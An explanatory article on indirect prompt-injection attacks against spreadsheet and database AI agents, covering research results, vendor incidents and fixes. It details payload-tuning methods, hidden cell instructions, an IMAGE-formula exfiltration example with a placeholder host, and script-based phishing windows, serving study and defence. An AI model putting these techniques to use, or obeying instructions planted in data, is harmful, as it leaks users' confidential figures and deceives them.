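# Security risks of AI agents that work with business spreadsheets and databases

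## How do AI agents work with tables, and why can a cell's text change what they do?

A tabular agent is a language model with tools that read, analyse or change tables. Companies use two main kinds. A spreadsheet assistant works inside Excel, Google Sheets or a similar product, where it answers questions about the open workbook, writes formulas and edits cells. A database agent, which many research papers call a data agent, writes and runs queries against a company's databases, often with Python code as well. Databricks, Snowflake and Google all sell one. Both kinds can make changes as well as answer questions. According to Microsoft's *Get started with Copilot in Excel*, Copilot opens by default in a mode that lets it edit the workbook directly.

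Business tables contain text from many sources, such as customers' complaints, suppliers' remarks and benchmarks copied from websites. An AI agent that works with tables receives this text through the same channel as its user's request, so someone who can write in a cell can sometimes change what the agent does.

### From a request to an answer

Suppose an analyst has a workbook with the company's revenue on one sheet and, on another, an industry table from a website. The analyst types "compare our revenue with this industry table". A language model can only produce text. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers who build on the company's Claude models, states that the model "never runs anything on its own". Ordinary software around the model does the running, in a loop:

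1. The software sends the model one long text, which contains the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), descriptions of the available tools, the analyst's request and usually some description of the workbook.
2. The model outputs a structured request for a tool, for example one that reads the first forty rows of the industry sheet.
3. The software runs the tool and receives the contents of the cells.
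4. The software adds those contents to the conversation and sends all of it to the model again.
5. The model outputs another tool request, perhaps to read the revenue sheet or to write a growth formula, and the loop repeats until the model outputs a final answer.

From the second pass on, the industry table and the analyst's request are part of the same text. Anthropic's interface puts the tool's result in a message with the role "user", inside a block labeled as a tool result.

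Products differ in when they send cell contents to the model. Pluto Security, a security firm, inspected the network traffic of the Claude add-in for Excel in 2026. The first request contained the names and sizes of the sheets but no cell contents. The add-in sent cells only when the model requested a range, and it sent none for a plain multiplication question. In Agent Mode, Microsoft's own agent in Excel, the software sends a compact "blueprint" with the user's prompt, as Microsoft's tmobrien explains in *Building Agent Mode in Excel* (2025). The blueprint summarises the layout, the values, the objects and the links between formulas. The agent then fetches more detail as it needs it, writes and runs code, checks the result and tries again.

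So in Claude for Excel, a payload (the text an attacker plants) has no effect until a question leads the agent to read its cell, while Microsoft's design may give the model some cell values from the start. The difference hardly matters for the analyst's request, because any agent has to read the industry table to make the comparison.

### Three routes from the table to the model

Large tables do not fit into a model's input, so agents select parts of them. *StruPhantom* (Feng and Pan, 2025), an early study of attacks on tabular agents, describes two ways to do this.

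One way for an agent to work with a table is through code. A program loads the file into memory as a DataFrame, a table object that it can filter and sort. It then picks out the relevant rows or columns and turns them into text for the model. The agent in *SpreadsheetBench 2* (2026), a test built on business spreadsheets, works by running one shell command at a time.

The second is similarity search. Software converts each row into a list of numbers that roughly captures its meaning and stores these lists in a vector database. It converts the user's question the same way, then gives the model the rows whose numbers are closest to the question's.

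Database agents take a third route, in which the model writes a query in SQL, the standard language for relational databases, and the database runs it and returns the resulting rows as text. *Data Agents Under Attack* (Wang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an analyst who asks for anomalies in fourth-quarter sales by region, which sets off a series of SQL queries, Python runs and file reads. The agent may also read descriptions of the database, such as the comments attached to columns, and an attacker can hide text there too.

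How an agent reads a table determines which text reaches the model. A query for total revenue by region returns only regions and totals, so a payload in a remarks column never reaches the model, although a false number in the revenue column still affects the result. A query that pulls whole rows includes the payload. If the agent uses similarity search, the planted row has to resemble the question to be retrieved. File formats also limit where an attacker can put text. Feng and Pan could use only text columns, because words in a numeric column risked an error when the program loaded the file. These limits make attacks harder, but nobody designed them as security controls, and in Feng and Pan's tests the planted text still got phishing links and code into agents' answers.

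### Indirect prompt injection

Greshake, Endres and colleagues named this kind of attack in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023). Earlier work on prompt injection had mostly assumed that the attacker was the user, typing text into a chatbot to get round its rules. Greshake and colleagues considered an attacker who never uses the chatbot and instead leaves instructions in a web page, email or file that the application will later retrieve. They demonstrated such attacks on Bing's GPT-4-powered chat and on applications they had built themselves.

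*Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026) describes a situation with three parties: a user with a legitimate task, an agent acting for that user, and an outside source that the agent consults. The agent follows instructions in the source's text even though the source has no authority to direct it.

Suppose whoever maintains the analyst's industry table has added an instruction to a remarks column, telling any AI agent that reads it to do something with the company's revenue figures. The analyst sees an ordinary benchmark table. On the second pass of the loop, the model receives the instruction together with the analyst's request. If it treats the instruction as part of that request, its next tool call carries out what the attacker wanted. The security firm PromptArmor demonstrated a similar case in *CellShock*, where outside growth benchmarks copied into a private financial model led Claude for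 Excel to leak that financial model's data.

Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, trace the problem to the text that the software assembles on each pass, which mixes instructions and data with no enforced boundary between them. They define an instruction injection as successful when the model's output is almost the same whether the attacker's text is in the data or in the instructions.

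Developers put labels around the user's words and around tool output, and they train models to give tool output no authority. But the labels are more text in the same stream, and models only learn to respond to them in training. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, measured how weak that learned response can be. They wrapped identical passages in different labels and trained a simple classifier to identify each passage's label from the model's internal activity alone. When they applied the classifier to an ordinary conversation, its scores depended almost entirely on style. Passages in the style of the model's own reasoning scored 85% as reasoning with the correct label, 83% with no label, and 85% when the label attributed them to the user.

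Those three figures come from one conversation and one fairly small open model, though Ye and colleagues found similar results in others. Over 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate also rose with confusion, from 2% where the classifier measured the least to 70% where it measured the most. That correlation could have another explanation, but a further experiment provides stronger evidence. When the researchers reworded forged reasoning to keep its argument but remove the imitated style, attack success fell from 61% to 10%.

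Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues (2025), in *ASIDE*, tested whether separating instructions from data would by itself make injections less successful. A given word enters an ordinary model as the same list of numbers whether it belongs to an instruction or to data. They changed this by applying a fixed rotation to the numbers for every word of data, then trained the models on everyday instruction-following examples that contained no attacks. The average success rate of injections fell from 14.7% to 4.9% on one benchmark and from 45.6% to 28.1% on another. The models were small by commercial standards. The result supports the view that missing separation lets injections succeed, but it also suggests that this kind of separation weakens the attack without ending it.

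Choi and colleagues point out that an agent could still be misled even if it perfectly separated instructions from data, because some data is less reliable than other data. In an email, for example, the system fills in the sender's address, but anyone can write the body. If text in the body imitates the format of the sender field, a model may mistake it for the system's own record. The agent still carries out the user's task, but with information from the attacker. In a table, text in one cell could similarly pass for a separate row from a reputable source.

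### Why the remedies for SQL injection and macros do not carry over

Many security teams will recognise the pattern from SQL injection. A vulnerable website builds a database command by pasting a visitor's input into it, so input with the right punctuation can end the data and begin a new command. Parameterised queries reliably prevent this. The program sends the command and the input separately, and the database engine never interprets the input as a command.

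*Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, warns against assuming that what is true of one problem is true of the other. It was written by David C, the centre's technical director for platforms research. A database engine handles instructions and data by different mechanisms, so engineers can enforce a boundary between them. A language model handles both by predicting the next token (a word or part of one) from all the text so far. David C proposes thinking of the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program with high privileges that someone with lower privileges tricks into using them. Engineers can repair a conventional one. With a language model, David C argues, they can make the trick less likely and limit the damage, but there is a good chance that there will never be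 a complete fix.

Summers, Mohammed and Wu (2025), in *Please Don't Kill My Vibe*, reach the same view from database research. Neutralising special characters is enough to stop injection in SQL because its parser follows a fixed grammar, but a model responds to meaning, which has no special characters to neutralise. In their example, a merchant writes a tea description that tells AI agents to delete the table of users, and an employee then asks an agent to summarise the products. The database works correctly when it returns the description as the text it stored. Parameterised queries would not prevent the attack, because the text becomes dangerous only afterwards, in the model's input.

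Attackers have used macros, small programs inside a workbook, to spread malware for decades. Office software can now block macros in files from the internet, and administrators can require signed ones. PromptArmor's *AI in Excel and Google Sheets*, a guide from May 2026, points out that these controls look for code. They don't block a malicious instruction in a cell because it is plain text. The instruction need not arrive with the file either, since anyone with editing rights can add it to a shared workbook months later. PromptArmor has a commercial interest in the subject, but Anthropic gives a similar warning about its own product. Claude for Excel does not support macros, yet Anthropic's *Use Claude for Excel* warns of instructions hidden in cells, formulas and comments. It tells customers not to use the add-in with downloaded templates, vendor files and other spreadsheets from untrusted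 outside sources. An analyst who compares the company with its industry would have to do much of that work without the add-in.

### Two kinds of attacker and what they can do

Wang and colleagues distinguish an outsider who supplies data from an insider who asks the questions. The outsider might be a vendor filling in a template, a customer typing into a free-text field, or a stranger who uploads a dataset to a public site. None of them needs access to the agent, because an honest employee triggers the attack later by asking an ordinary question. The insider is a dishonest employee or someone who has taken over an employee's account. In *Agentic AI Security*, Chhabra, Datta and colleagues (2025) similarly distinguish direct injection, where the user is the attacker, from indirect injection, where the attacker owns or supplies the data.

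An insider may not need to plant text in the data. Many database agents connect through a service account, a shared login that can read far more than most employees are allowed to, so the insider can ask the agent for a table that their own account can't open. Screening incoming data for planted text doesn't prevent this.

Between them, these attackers can cause six kinds of harm. An agent can put a phishing link, which leads to a fake site that collects passwords, in an answer its user has good reason to trust. It can give the user harmful code or run such code itself. It can leak private data (known as exfiltration), for instance by inserting a network formula, which is a spreadsheet formula that contacts an outside server, and putting confidential figures in the web address. It can report false figures, as in Wang and colleagues' example of a planted file that contains an instruction to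 multiply all revenue by 1.5. It can damage records. In Anthropic's testing of Claude for Excel, manipulation in some cases led the add-in to alter financial data or delete it across several sheets. Finally, it can waste computing resources, since a request to compare every customer with every similar one in a table of 30 million rows can exhaust a database's memory without breaking any access rules.

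## Can text in a table make an agent hand its user a phishing link or harmful code?

Feng and Pan showed in April 2025 that instructions planted in an ordinary table can make an agent recommend a made-up website to its user or put unrelated code in its answer. Both attacks worked on agents built on four different language models. When software automatically improved the planted instructions, the link attack succeeded in 12.5% to 94.4% of attempts, depending on the agent, and the code attack in 6.25% to 87.5%.

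All four models are long out of date, and no later study seems to have repeated the test with 2026 models. More recent evidence on phishing links comes from assistants that read web pages and calendar entries. Those cases make the risk from tables more believable, but they don't show how often text in a table would have this effect.

### A poisoned public dataset

The attacker in this study is an outsider who adds payloads to a dataset and uploads it to a free data-sharing website. This attacker doesn't know what an analyst who downloads the file will ask, and needs no inside knowledge of the model. Feng and Pan assume only that the attacker can see the model's outputs and buy developer access to the same model, which many AI companies sell.

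The analyst probably wouldn't notice the payload first, because the table in the study had 891 rows and 12 columns, or more than 10,000 cells. Office files can also contain text that they don't show to a human reader. *When File Ingestion Misleads Language Models* (Li, 2026) examined ten programs that extract text from Word, Excel and PowerPoint files, and found 19 kinds of location where at least one program picks up such hidden text. Li's own attacks contain no instructions and work by making the model misread the document, but an attacker could put an instruction in the same places.

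It is hard to know how often anyone poisons a dataset like this. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026) studied how common planted instructions are on the open web, but nobody seems to have done the same for public datasets.

Feng and Pan call their work the first in-depth study of these attacks on agents that take tables as input. Yi, Kiciman and colleagues (2023) had already tested 25 language models without tools in *Benchmarking and Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on Large Language Models*. They planted instructions in tables and asked the models questions about them. GPT-4 followed the planted instructions in 35% of cases and GPT-3.5-turbo in 23%, while the average over all 25 models was about 8%. The test software put the table directly into the prompt, so the planted instructions always reached the model, whereas an agent may never read the row that contains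 them.

### How the attack improves its own payloads

For each of the attacker's goals, Feng and Pan wrote eight payload templates by hand, in direct and forceful language. They then let software improve the templates in a loop:

1. The software selects a set of templates that looks promising.
2. A language model rewrites a template from the set. It can write a new version with the same meaning, merge several templates, lengthen one, shorten one or rephrase one. It must keep the essential part, such as the web address.
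3. Another model checks whether the new version still serves the attacker's goal. If the wording has drifted too far, the software goes back to the rewriting step.
4. The software tries the new version on a stand-in agent, which the attacker has built to resemble the real target, and checks whether the wanted content appears in the answer.
5. If the success rate is too low, a further model reads the stand-in agent's reasoning and revises the template. The reasoning might reveal, for example, that the agent filters out irrelevant text before it extracts data.
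6. The improved template replaces the weakest one in the set. The software records the set's new average success rate and starts again.

The stand-in agent makes the fifth step possible because the attacker runs it and can read everything it writes before its final answer. With someone else's agent, the attacker sees only the final answers.

The selection step uses Monte Carlo tree search, a method best known from programs that play Go. The software keeps a tree of template sets, in which each set's parent is the set it was made from. A set's score is its average success rate so far plus a bonus that favors sets the search has rarely visited. The bonus is √(2 log(P/N)), where P is the number of visits to the parent set and N is the number of visits to the set itself.

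Suppose the parent has had 20 visits. One descendant has had ten visits and succeeds 60% of the time, so its score is 0.6 plus a bonus of about 1.18, or 1.78. Another has had two visits and succeeds 40% of the time, so its score is 0.4 plus a bonus of about 2.15, or 2.55. The software works on the second set next, although its success rate is lower. If both had the same number of visits, their bonuses would be equal and the more successful set would have the higher score. The bonus stops the search from settling too early on a template that did well only in its first few trials.

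The search greatly improved the templates, raising the success rate of the link templates to nearly 90% by the twentieth round. Rewriting alone also helped, but adding revisions based on the stand-in agent's reasoning worked better for all three goals. The code templates were the hardest to improve.

### Results for eight agents

Feng and Pan built eight target agents, two from each of four models: Alibaba's Qwen-turbo, Zhipu's GLM-4, OpenAI's GPT-3.5-turbo and Anthropic's Claude 3.5 Haiku. One agent in each pair filtered the table as a DataFrame, and the other used similarity search. The table was the Titanic passenger list, a public dataset, and the researchers inserted the templates at random positions in it.

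The attacks had three goals. The link attack was meant to make the agent tell its user about a website that doesn't exist. The sentence attack was meant to make it output a fixed, harmless sentence, a simple test of whether the attacker controls the answer. The code attack was meant to make it output a line of code that adds two numbers. The attack success rate is the share of templates that produced the content the attacker wanted.

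| Model | How the agent reads the table | Link, handwritten (%) | Link, optimised (%) | Sentence, optimised (%) | Code, optimised (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-turbo | DataFrame | 50.00 | 89.58 | 83.33 | 87.50 |
| Qwen-turbo | Similarity search | 75.00 | 94.40 | 100.00 | 87.50 |
| GLM-4 | DataFrame | 50.00 | 50.00 | 93.75 | 18.75 |
| GLM-4 | Similarity search | 43.75 | 68.75 | 87.50 | 72.22 |
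| GPT-3.5-turbo | DataFrame | 0.00 | 12.50 | 31.25 | 6.25 |
| GPT-3.5-turbo | Similarity search | 43.75 | 93.75 | 100.00 | 37.50 |
| Claude 3.5 Haiku | DataFrame | 12.50 | 25.00 | 25.00 | 9.50 |
| Claude 3.5 Haiku | Similarity search | 25.00 | 43.75 | 46.88 | 24.55 |

How an agent read the table mattered about as much as its model. Optimised link attacks succeeded 75% of the time on average against the similarity-search agents and 44% of the time against the DataFrame agents. For code, the averages were 55% and 31%.

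GPT-3.5-turbo is the clearest case. The optimised link attack almost always failed when the agent queried a DataFrame, but it succeeded 93.75% of the time when the agent used similarity search. Feng and Pan interpret the low DataFrame figure as resistance by the agent. That is true of the agent as a whole, but the similarity search result shows that the model itself was vulnerable. The DataFrame agent's filters probably often left the payload out, so the model never saw it. The success rate can't confirm this, because it counts a payload that the model ignored and a payload that the model never received as the same failure. Anyone testing their own agent should record the two separately, because a vulnerable model can look safe if the test question happens to filter out the payload.

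These figures come from plain-text CSV files, but most business users will care more about Excel files. In a further test on Excel workbooks, the optimised link attack succeeded 70% of the time and the code attack 43.75%, compared with 33.75% and 13.75% for the handwritten versions. Link attacks had similar success rates in two other structured data formats, 60% in XML and 63% in JSON. Code attacks succeeded 40.25% of the time in XML files but only 12.5% in JSON files.

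### Where the figure of 92% comes from

In one scenario cited in the study's introduction, optimised payloads reached an average success rate of 92.0% "across two real-world tabular agents", compared with 62.5% for handwritten ones. The introduction doesn't name the agents, but the figures match the link attack on the two Qwen-turbo agents, where optimised payloads averaged 91.99% (89.58% and 94.40%) and handwritten ones averaged 62.5% (50% and 75%).

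Qwen-turbo was also the model in the stand-in agent. So the headline describes how well the attack worked against the very model that the researchers had tuned it on. The averages for all eight agents are much lower:

- Optimised: 89.58 + 94.40 + 50.00 + 68.75 + 12.50 + 93.75 + 25.00 + 43.75 = 477.73, which divided by 8 is about 59.7%.
- Handwritten: 50.00 + 75.00 + 50.00 + 43.75 + 0.00 + 43.75 + 12.50 + 25.00 = 300.00, which divided by 8 is 37.5%.

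Without the two Qwen-turbo agents, the averages fall to 49.0% and 29.2%.

The better estimate for the study's own scenario is 49%, because an attacker who uploads a poisoned dataset to a public website doesn't know who will download it or which model will read it. The higher number is reasonable for an attacker who knows which model a company uses, since the threat model lets the attacker buy access to that model and tune the payload on it. The 49% figure also shows that payloads tuned on one model work on others, though less often.

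According to the abstract, the attack achieves "over 50% higher success rates than baselines". For links, this holds as a relative increase across the eight agents, since 59.7% is 59% higher than the baseline's 37.5%. The difference is 22 percentage points.

These figures are rough because each goal had only eight templates, and many results are multiples of 6.25%, which suggests about sixteen trials for each result. With sixteen trials, a measured rate of 50% could mean a true rate anywhere from about 25% to 75%. The gap between GPT-3.5-turbo's two agents is too large to be chance, but many smaller differences in the table could be.

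Feng and Pan also demonstrated the link attack on Doubao and Coze, two ByteDance platforms where customers can build their own agents. For ethical reasons, they built the target applications themselves. They present snapshots of successful attacks but no success rate. The platforms' built-in protections did not stop the attack in those cases, though this doesn't show that any company's existing agent was vulnerable. Feng and Pan also write that the agents successfully lured users to click, but they did not measure clicks.

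### Showing a link or code is different from acting on it

A phishing link in an answer does no harm until someone opens it and, usually, types in a password, and harmful code does none until someone copies and runs it. But an agent with a browser can open the link itself, and one with a Python tool can run the code, before anyone has a chance to stop and think.

Feng and Pan describe their code attack as an attempt to make the agent execute arbitrary code, but they counted an attempt as a success when the intended content appeared in the agent's answer. The success rates of 6.25% to 87.5% therefore measure how often agents showed the code, not how often they would have run it.

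Their planted code was also just a sum, which gives a model no reason to refuse. Yi and colleagues found that GPT-4 followed planted instructions less often when the code would change the user's system or data than when it would only gather information. They think GPT-4 understood the code well enough to recognise the intent. Harmful code would probably have succeeded less often in the Titanic table than the sum did. The made-up web address is a weak test for a similar reason, since a link filter can't have a record of a site that has never existed.

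In *INFUSE*, Nguyen, Guo and colleagues (2026) counted in nearly the opposite way. An attack succeeded only if the planted text influenced what the agent did or decided, so an agent that merely quoted the text passed. They tested 19 models as command-line agents, on tasks from debugging to file management. The average success rate was 19.6%, with individual models ranging from 3.2% to 41.9%. These figures are not evidence that agents have become safer since the study that found 59.7% for links, because the tasks were different and an agent that repeated a planted address to its user could fail in one study and pass in the other.

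*AgentVigil* (2025) describes a product review that led a web agent to visit an address the attacker had chosen. The researchers posted the review from an ordinary customer account on a local copy of an online shop. The user had asked the agent to find a screen protector and list the reviewers who praised its resistance to fingerprints. Many companies export reviews like this one into tables, where a tabular agent that can also browse would read the same text.

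This kind of attack may work less well in a table than on a web page, because a cell can easily hold a web address but not a working web page button. In *It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* (2025), 735 of 948 successful attacks on web agents used a button and 213 used a hyperlink. In a comparison of 35 pairs of attacks on the same task, the button version succeeded 66% of the time with Gemini 2.5 Flash and the link version 9%.

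Phishing links and harmful code also differ in whether the user sees anything. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports on a public competition with 41 scenarios, in which an attack counted only if the agent took the harmful action and also hid this in its final answer. An attacker who wants the user to click a link can't hide it, so the user at least has something to be suspicious of. An agent that has run an attacker's code, however, can still return a normal summary.

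For tables, the more serious danger is therefore an agent running planted code. Newer evidence comes from Wang and colleagues, who planted code in data for a database agent to run. The attack worked at least some of the time with each of the four models they tried in that agent.

### How an assistant makes a link look trustworthy

Most people will never look at a web address in row 600 of a workbook's remarks column, but if an agent repeats it in an answer, it looks like advice from a tool the user has chosen to rely on.

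The best recent demonstration involves web pages. *ChatGPhish*, published by the security firm Permiso in May 2026, describes an attack on ChatGPT's page summaries. The researchers added instructions to a GitHub project page, opened it in Firefox and used the browser's option to have ChatGPT summarise it. ChatGPT produced a real summary of the project, followed by a notice that a new device had joined the user's account, with a clickable link to the attacker's site. Nothing indicated that the link came from the page.

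This attack works only if the model follows the planted instruction and the application turns the result into something clickable. Models format their answers in Markdown, a notation that uses punctuation marks to turn text into headings, links or images. According to Permiso, ChatGPT's website turned Markdown from the summarised page into working links and images. The same injection would be much less convincing if the application showed the addresses as plain text or labelled where they came from.

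ChatGPT's website loaded images automatically, so the attacker's server received the user's IP address, browser details and the exact time of the answer without a click. The researchers also had ChatGPT display a QR code. A user who scans one opens the link on a phone, where the desktop browser's warnings and the company's link filters no longer apply.

Permiso reported the problem to OpenAI on April 29, 2026. Permiso says its first report came back as not reproducible. A fuller version, sent on May 1, was first marked "Not Applicable" and later marked a duplicate of an earlier report, so someone else had apparently already found the problem. Permiso, which sells security products, gives examples from two pages but no success rate. The examples show that the attack was possible in a major product in 2026, but not how reliably it worked.

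A calendar entry is closer to a row in a table, because it is a record with a few short fields that an outsider can fill in by sending an invitation. In *Invitation Is All You Need!* (2025), researchers put instructions in the title of a meeting. The victim asked Google's Gemini about upcoming meetings, which brought the title into the conversation. When the victim thanked the assistant, it recommended a Kickstarter project chosen by the attacker and gave a clickable link. The researchers note that the link could just as easily lead to a page that collects passwords or credit card numbers.

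The delay matters for tables too, because an analyst might check the agent's answer against the workbook, find it correct, and then receive the link one message later, when nothing obviously connects it to the file. Spreadsheet assistants may also be able to present a fake page in more elaborate ways, such as the phishing windows that researchers have produced in Google Sheets.

Neither demonstration measured how many people would click, so a link that appears 60% of the time might fool nearly everyone who sees it or hardly anyone. *Are You Sure?* (2026) presents a platform that could measure this. It records what people do as they carry out realistic tasks with an agent, without knowing that the experiment is about security. *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* also measures whether the recipient approves an action the agent recommends, but its recipients are simulated. Links that originate in a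 table still need to be tested with real people.

### Why there is no current rate for tables

Since 2025, research on tables and research on phishing have mostly proceeded separately. Wang and colleagues attacked database agents to make them take unauthorised actions, report wrong results or waste resources, but did not try to make them show users a link. *TrustDABench* (2026) alters tables to test whether models still analyse them correctly, for example by adding summary rows or simulated records that a careful analyst would leave out. Li tested current versions of ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and Microsoft 365 Copilot on Office files that contained misleading content but no planted instructions. *LoginTrap* (2026) studies phishing-style attacks on agents that browse the web.

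Nobody can say how often a current spreadsheet assistant would pass on a phishing link from a cell. The 2025 rates are a poor guide, because the current rate could be higher or lower. Developers have since trained newer models to resist injections, which may well defeat the old payloads. But those payloads came from a search tuned on Qwen-turbo. An attacker today would run the search again on a current model, so a fair test would have to do the same.

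## What have researchers done to the AI assistants inside Excel and Google Sheets?

Between November 2025 and May 2026, PromptArmor got three commercial spreadsheet assistants to send confidential figures to a server it controlled. Claude for Excel and Ramp's Sheets AI each leaked data from a financial model through a single formula. ChatGPT for Google Sheets ran a script that copied 12 workbooks and could also open phishing windows. All three vendors changed their products afterwards.

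PromptArmor sells a service that monitors the AI products its customers buy, so it benefits when companies worry about those products. The flaws were almost certainly real, since all three vendors responded with changes. But PromptArmor chose the conditions for its demonstrations. It doesn't report how many attempts failed, so nobody can work out a success rate, and it doesn't describe any real victims.

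The first case is the *CellShock* attack on Claude for Excel. PromptArmor's *Ramp’s Sheets AI Exfiltrates Financials* describes a nearly identical attack on a web spreadsheet with a built-in agent from Ramp, a corporate card company. PromptArmor followed with *ChatGPT for Google Sheets Exfiltrates Workbooks* on May 27, 2026.

| | Claude for Excel | Ramp's Sheets AI | ChatGPT for Google Sheets |
|---|---|---|---|
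| PromptArmor's report to the vendor | November 2025 | February 19, 2026 | May 8, 2026 |
| User's request | Summarise the model against industry data and make a visualization | Compare the model with industry data | Update the model by following the workflow in the imported sheet |
| What the agent did | Inserted an image formula | Inserted an image formula | Ran an outside script |
| Approval prompt | Appeared, but hid the formula | None | None, even with automatic edits off |
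| What leaked | A summary of one financial model | Figures from one financial model | 12 workbooks |
| Vendor's fix | A red warning with the full formula, and a new default model | Fixed on March 16, without published details | The model can no longer write scripts |

The setup was almost the same each time. An analyst added an outside dataset to a workbook with confidential projections and asked the agent for help with both. The dataset contained a payload in text the same color as its background.

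The payload for Claude contained disguised instructions for leaking data. They described a private image generator that the agent could supposedly use by inserting a formula, and directed the agent to use it when the user wanted a visualization. The attack would work only if the analyst asked for one, but people who compare their company with its industry often want a chart, so an attacker could reasonably expect the request.

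### How an image formula leaks figures

Excel and Google Sheets both have an IMAGE function, which loads a picture from a web address and displays it in a cell. To get the picture, the spreadsheet sends the address to a server. An address can contain extra text after a question mark. Websites use this text for things like search terms, but an attacker can use it to receive data.

Suppose a workbook contains three private forecasts for next year: revenue of $48 million in cell B2, growth of 31% in B3 and an operating margin of 12% in B4. The leak works like this:

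1. The agent reads a payload that tells it to add a picture from a certain server and to include the forecasts in the picture's address.
2. It reads the three cells and writes the address `https://pictures.example/chart.png?data=48-31-12`. (This is a placeholder, because nobody can register a name that ends in ".example".)
3. It puts an IMAGE formula with that address into an empty cell.
4. Excel calculates the formula and asks the server for the picture.
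5. The server records the full request, including the numbers 48, 31 and 12, and returns a blank picture.

The attacker has the figures as soon as the request arrives, even if the requested picture doesn't exist, so deleting the formula later doesn't help.

In the attack on Claude for Excel, the picture was a single white pixel, so cell A57 looked empty even though Claude told the user it had inserted a professional financial dashboard there. PromptArmor's server log contained revenue projections, cash flow growth and operating margins.

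A formula can put the figures into the address by referring to their cells, or the agent can write the values out itself. PromptArmor's payload used the second method, partly because Excel on a Mac lacks the function that makes text safe for use in a web address. This method is also harder to detect. The finished formula contains no reference to the confidential sheet, so a tool that traces links between cells would not connect the two. The agent can also summarise a whole financial model before it writes the address, which an ordinary formula can't do.

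IMAGE is one of several network formulas. PromptArmor's guide to AI in spreadsheets also lists WEBSERVICE in Excel, and IMPORTDATA and IMPORTXML in Google Sheets. HYPERLINK is another, but it leaks nothing until someone clicks the link.

Excel can warn users before a workbook connects to an outside service. The warning didn't appear in PromptArmor's test because the researchers had created the workbook on their own computer. Excel also showed no warning if the user had marked the file or its folder as trusted, or had allowed this type of content for the session or permanently. Because these checks depend on where the file came from and what the user accepted earlier, an analyst's own financial model passes them even after the analyst has pasted in a stranger's data.

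In some runs, Claude also accidentally removed the evidence. It inserted the malicious image, checked the cell before the image had loaded, and concluded that something had gone wrong. It then placed an ordinary Excel chart over the same cells. This gave the user the chart they had asked for, but the figures had already leaked. Someone investigating later would find nothing suspicious in the workbook and would need a record of network traffic or of the agent's edits. Claude for Excel can now log its actions in what Anthropic describes as a separate tab in the workbook, but users have to turn the log on or ask for it.

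### What the approval prompts showed

The first version of Claude for Excel asked for permission before it inserted the formula, but the approval prompt didn't show the formula, the outside address or the figures in that address. The prompt was titled "Add visualization" and described the action as setting a cell range. The analyst had just asked for a visualization, so they had good reason to approve.

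Anthropic had already warned in its October 2025 help page, *Claude for Excel*, that attackers could extract sensitive information through formulas. The page listed IMAGE among the functions that users could approve. It also advised against using the add-in with data from untrusted sources, which the user in PromptArmor's demonstration did anyway. But the approval prompt left out the information that a user would have needed to refuse.

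Ramp's agent could edit the spreadsheet without approval, and it inserted the malicious formula as soon as the user asked for a comparison.

ChatGPT for Google Sheets has a setting called "Apply edits automatically". A user who turns it off expects to approve each change. PromptArmor turned it off, but the script still ran without an approval prompt. A commenter on the technology forum Hacker News suggested that the setting may not have covered the script because sending data out doesn't edit the sheet. That might explain the leak, but PromptArmor found that the attacker's scripts could also change workbooks.

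In March, OpenAI told customers in *Introducing ChatGPT for Excel and new financial data integrations* (2026) that ChatGPT would ask for permission before changing an Excel workbook, so that they could review each step. According to PromptArmor's guide, however, the Google Sheets version, released in beta on April 22, asks for approval to edit only once per session, so a user who accepts one harmless edit also accepts later ones that they haven't seen.

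### Why the script did more damage than a formula

A formula can send only the data that fits in a web address. Each address gives the attacker one request, and the agent has to decide what to include. A script is a program, so it can read a whole workbook, send it out, search for more data and repeat.

The payload led ChatGPT to run an attacker-controlled script written in Apps Script, Google's language for automating Sheets and its other office products. The script ran with the permissions the user had given the add-on, which covered other spreadsheets in the user's Google account as well as the open one. By contrast, Anthropic states that Claude for Excel can read only the open workbook, which limits what a formula attack on it could leak.

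PromptArmor's script first copied the financial model, then followed a link in it to a budgeting spreadsheet and copied that too. It kept searching the stolen data for links until it had copied 12 workbooks. The attacker didn't need to know that any of these files existed. Many companies link their workbooks this way, because a budget draws on a forecast and the forecast draws on sales data, so a single payload could reach many workbooks.

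A better language model might have refused to run the script, but once the script had started, the model couldn't refuse individual steps because it wasn't carrying them out. The user couldn't interrupt them with the stop button in ChatGPT's sidebar either, because it did not stop a script that was already running.

The script could also open two kinds of phishing window. One was a pop-up that loaded the attacker's website and asked for a password. The other was a copy of the ChatGPT sidebar that covered the real one. The fake sidebar could edit the sheet as ChatGPT does, so it could work mostly as normal while recording everything the user typed. It could also ask the user to sign in to OpenAI again or to "reconnect" other apps, which would give the attacker access to those apps. These windows are much more convincing than a link in an answer because they appear inside Google Sheets, where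 the browser's address bar doesn't show that they are fake, and because people are used to add-ons asking them to sign in again.

The add-on had more than 185,000 downloads by the time PromptArmor published its findings, less than a month after launch. That number gives an idea of how many people could have been exposed, but there is no evidence that anyone attacked them.

Another Hacker News commenter objected that PromptArmor's demonstration was unfair because the user in it had asked ChatGPT to follow "the step-by-step workflow in the comp sheet", the imported sheet that contained the payload. The commenter argued that the attacker had therefore manipulated the user, not the model.

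Chang, Nikolić and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil is in the Context*, point out that the same sentence in a document can be an attack or a legitimate command, depending on whether the user asked the agent to carry out the document's instructions. The user's request did make this attack easier, and the attack would probably work less often if the request mentioned only the data. But the user had asked for an updated financial model, and any authority that request gave the sheet did not extend to copying other workbooks to a stranger's server. Chang and colleagues similarly argue that even a trusted source has authority only within the limits of the user's task. The request was also an ordinary one, since employees regularly follow instructions in templates.

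### What the vendors changed

Anthropic acted fastest. PromptArmor documented the attack on November 18, 2025, during the private beta. By November 24, when PromptArmor tested the public beta, Anthropic had added an approval prompt for formulas that contact outside servers. The prompt shows the full formula in a red warning, so a careful user can see the strange address and the company's figures in it.

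PromptArmor called this a great step in the right direction but found gaps in it:

- The warning did not always appear. PromptArmor suspects that a language model decides when to show it.
- The warning did not display invisible Unicode characters, which are valid characters that have no visible shape. An agent could encode the stolen figures in such characters. The user would see a harmless address, and the attacker could still decode the figures.
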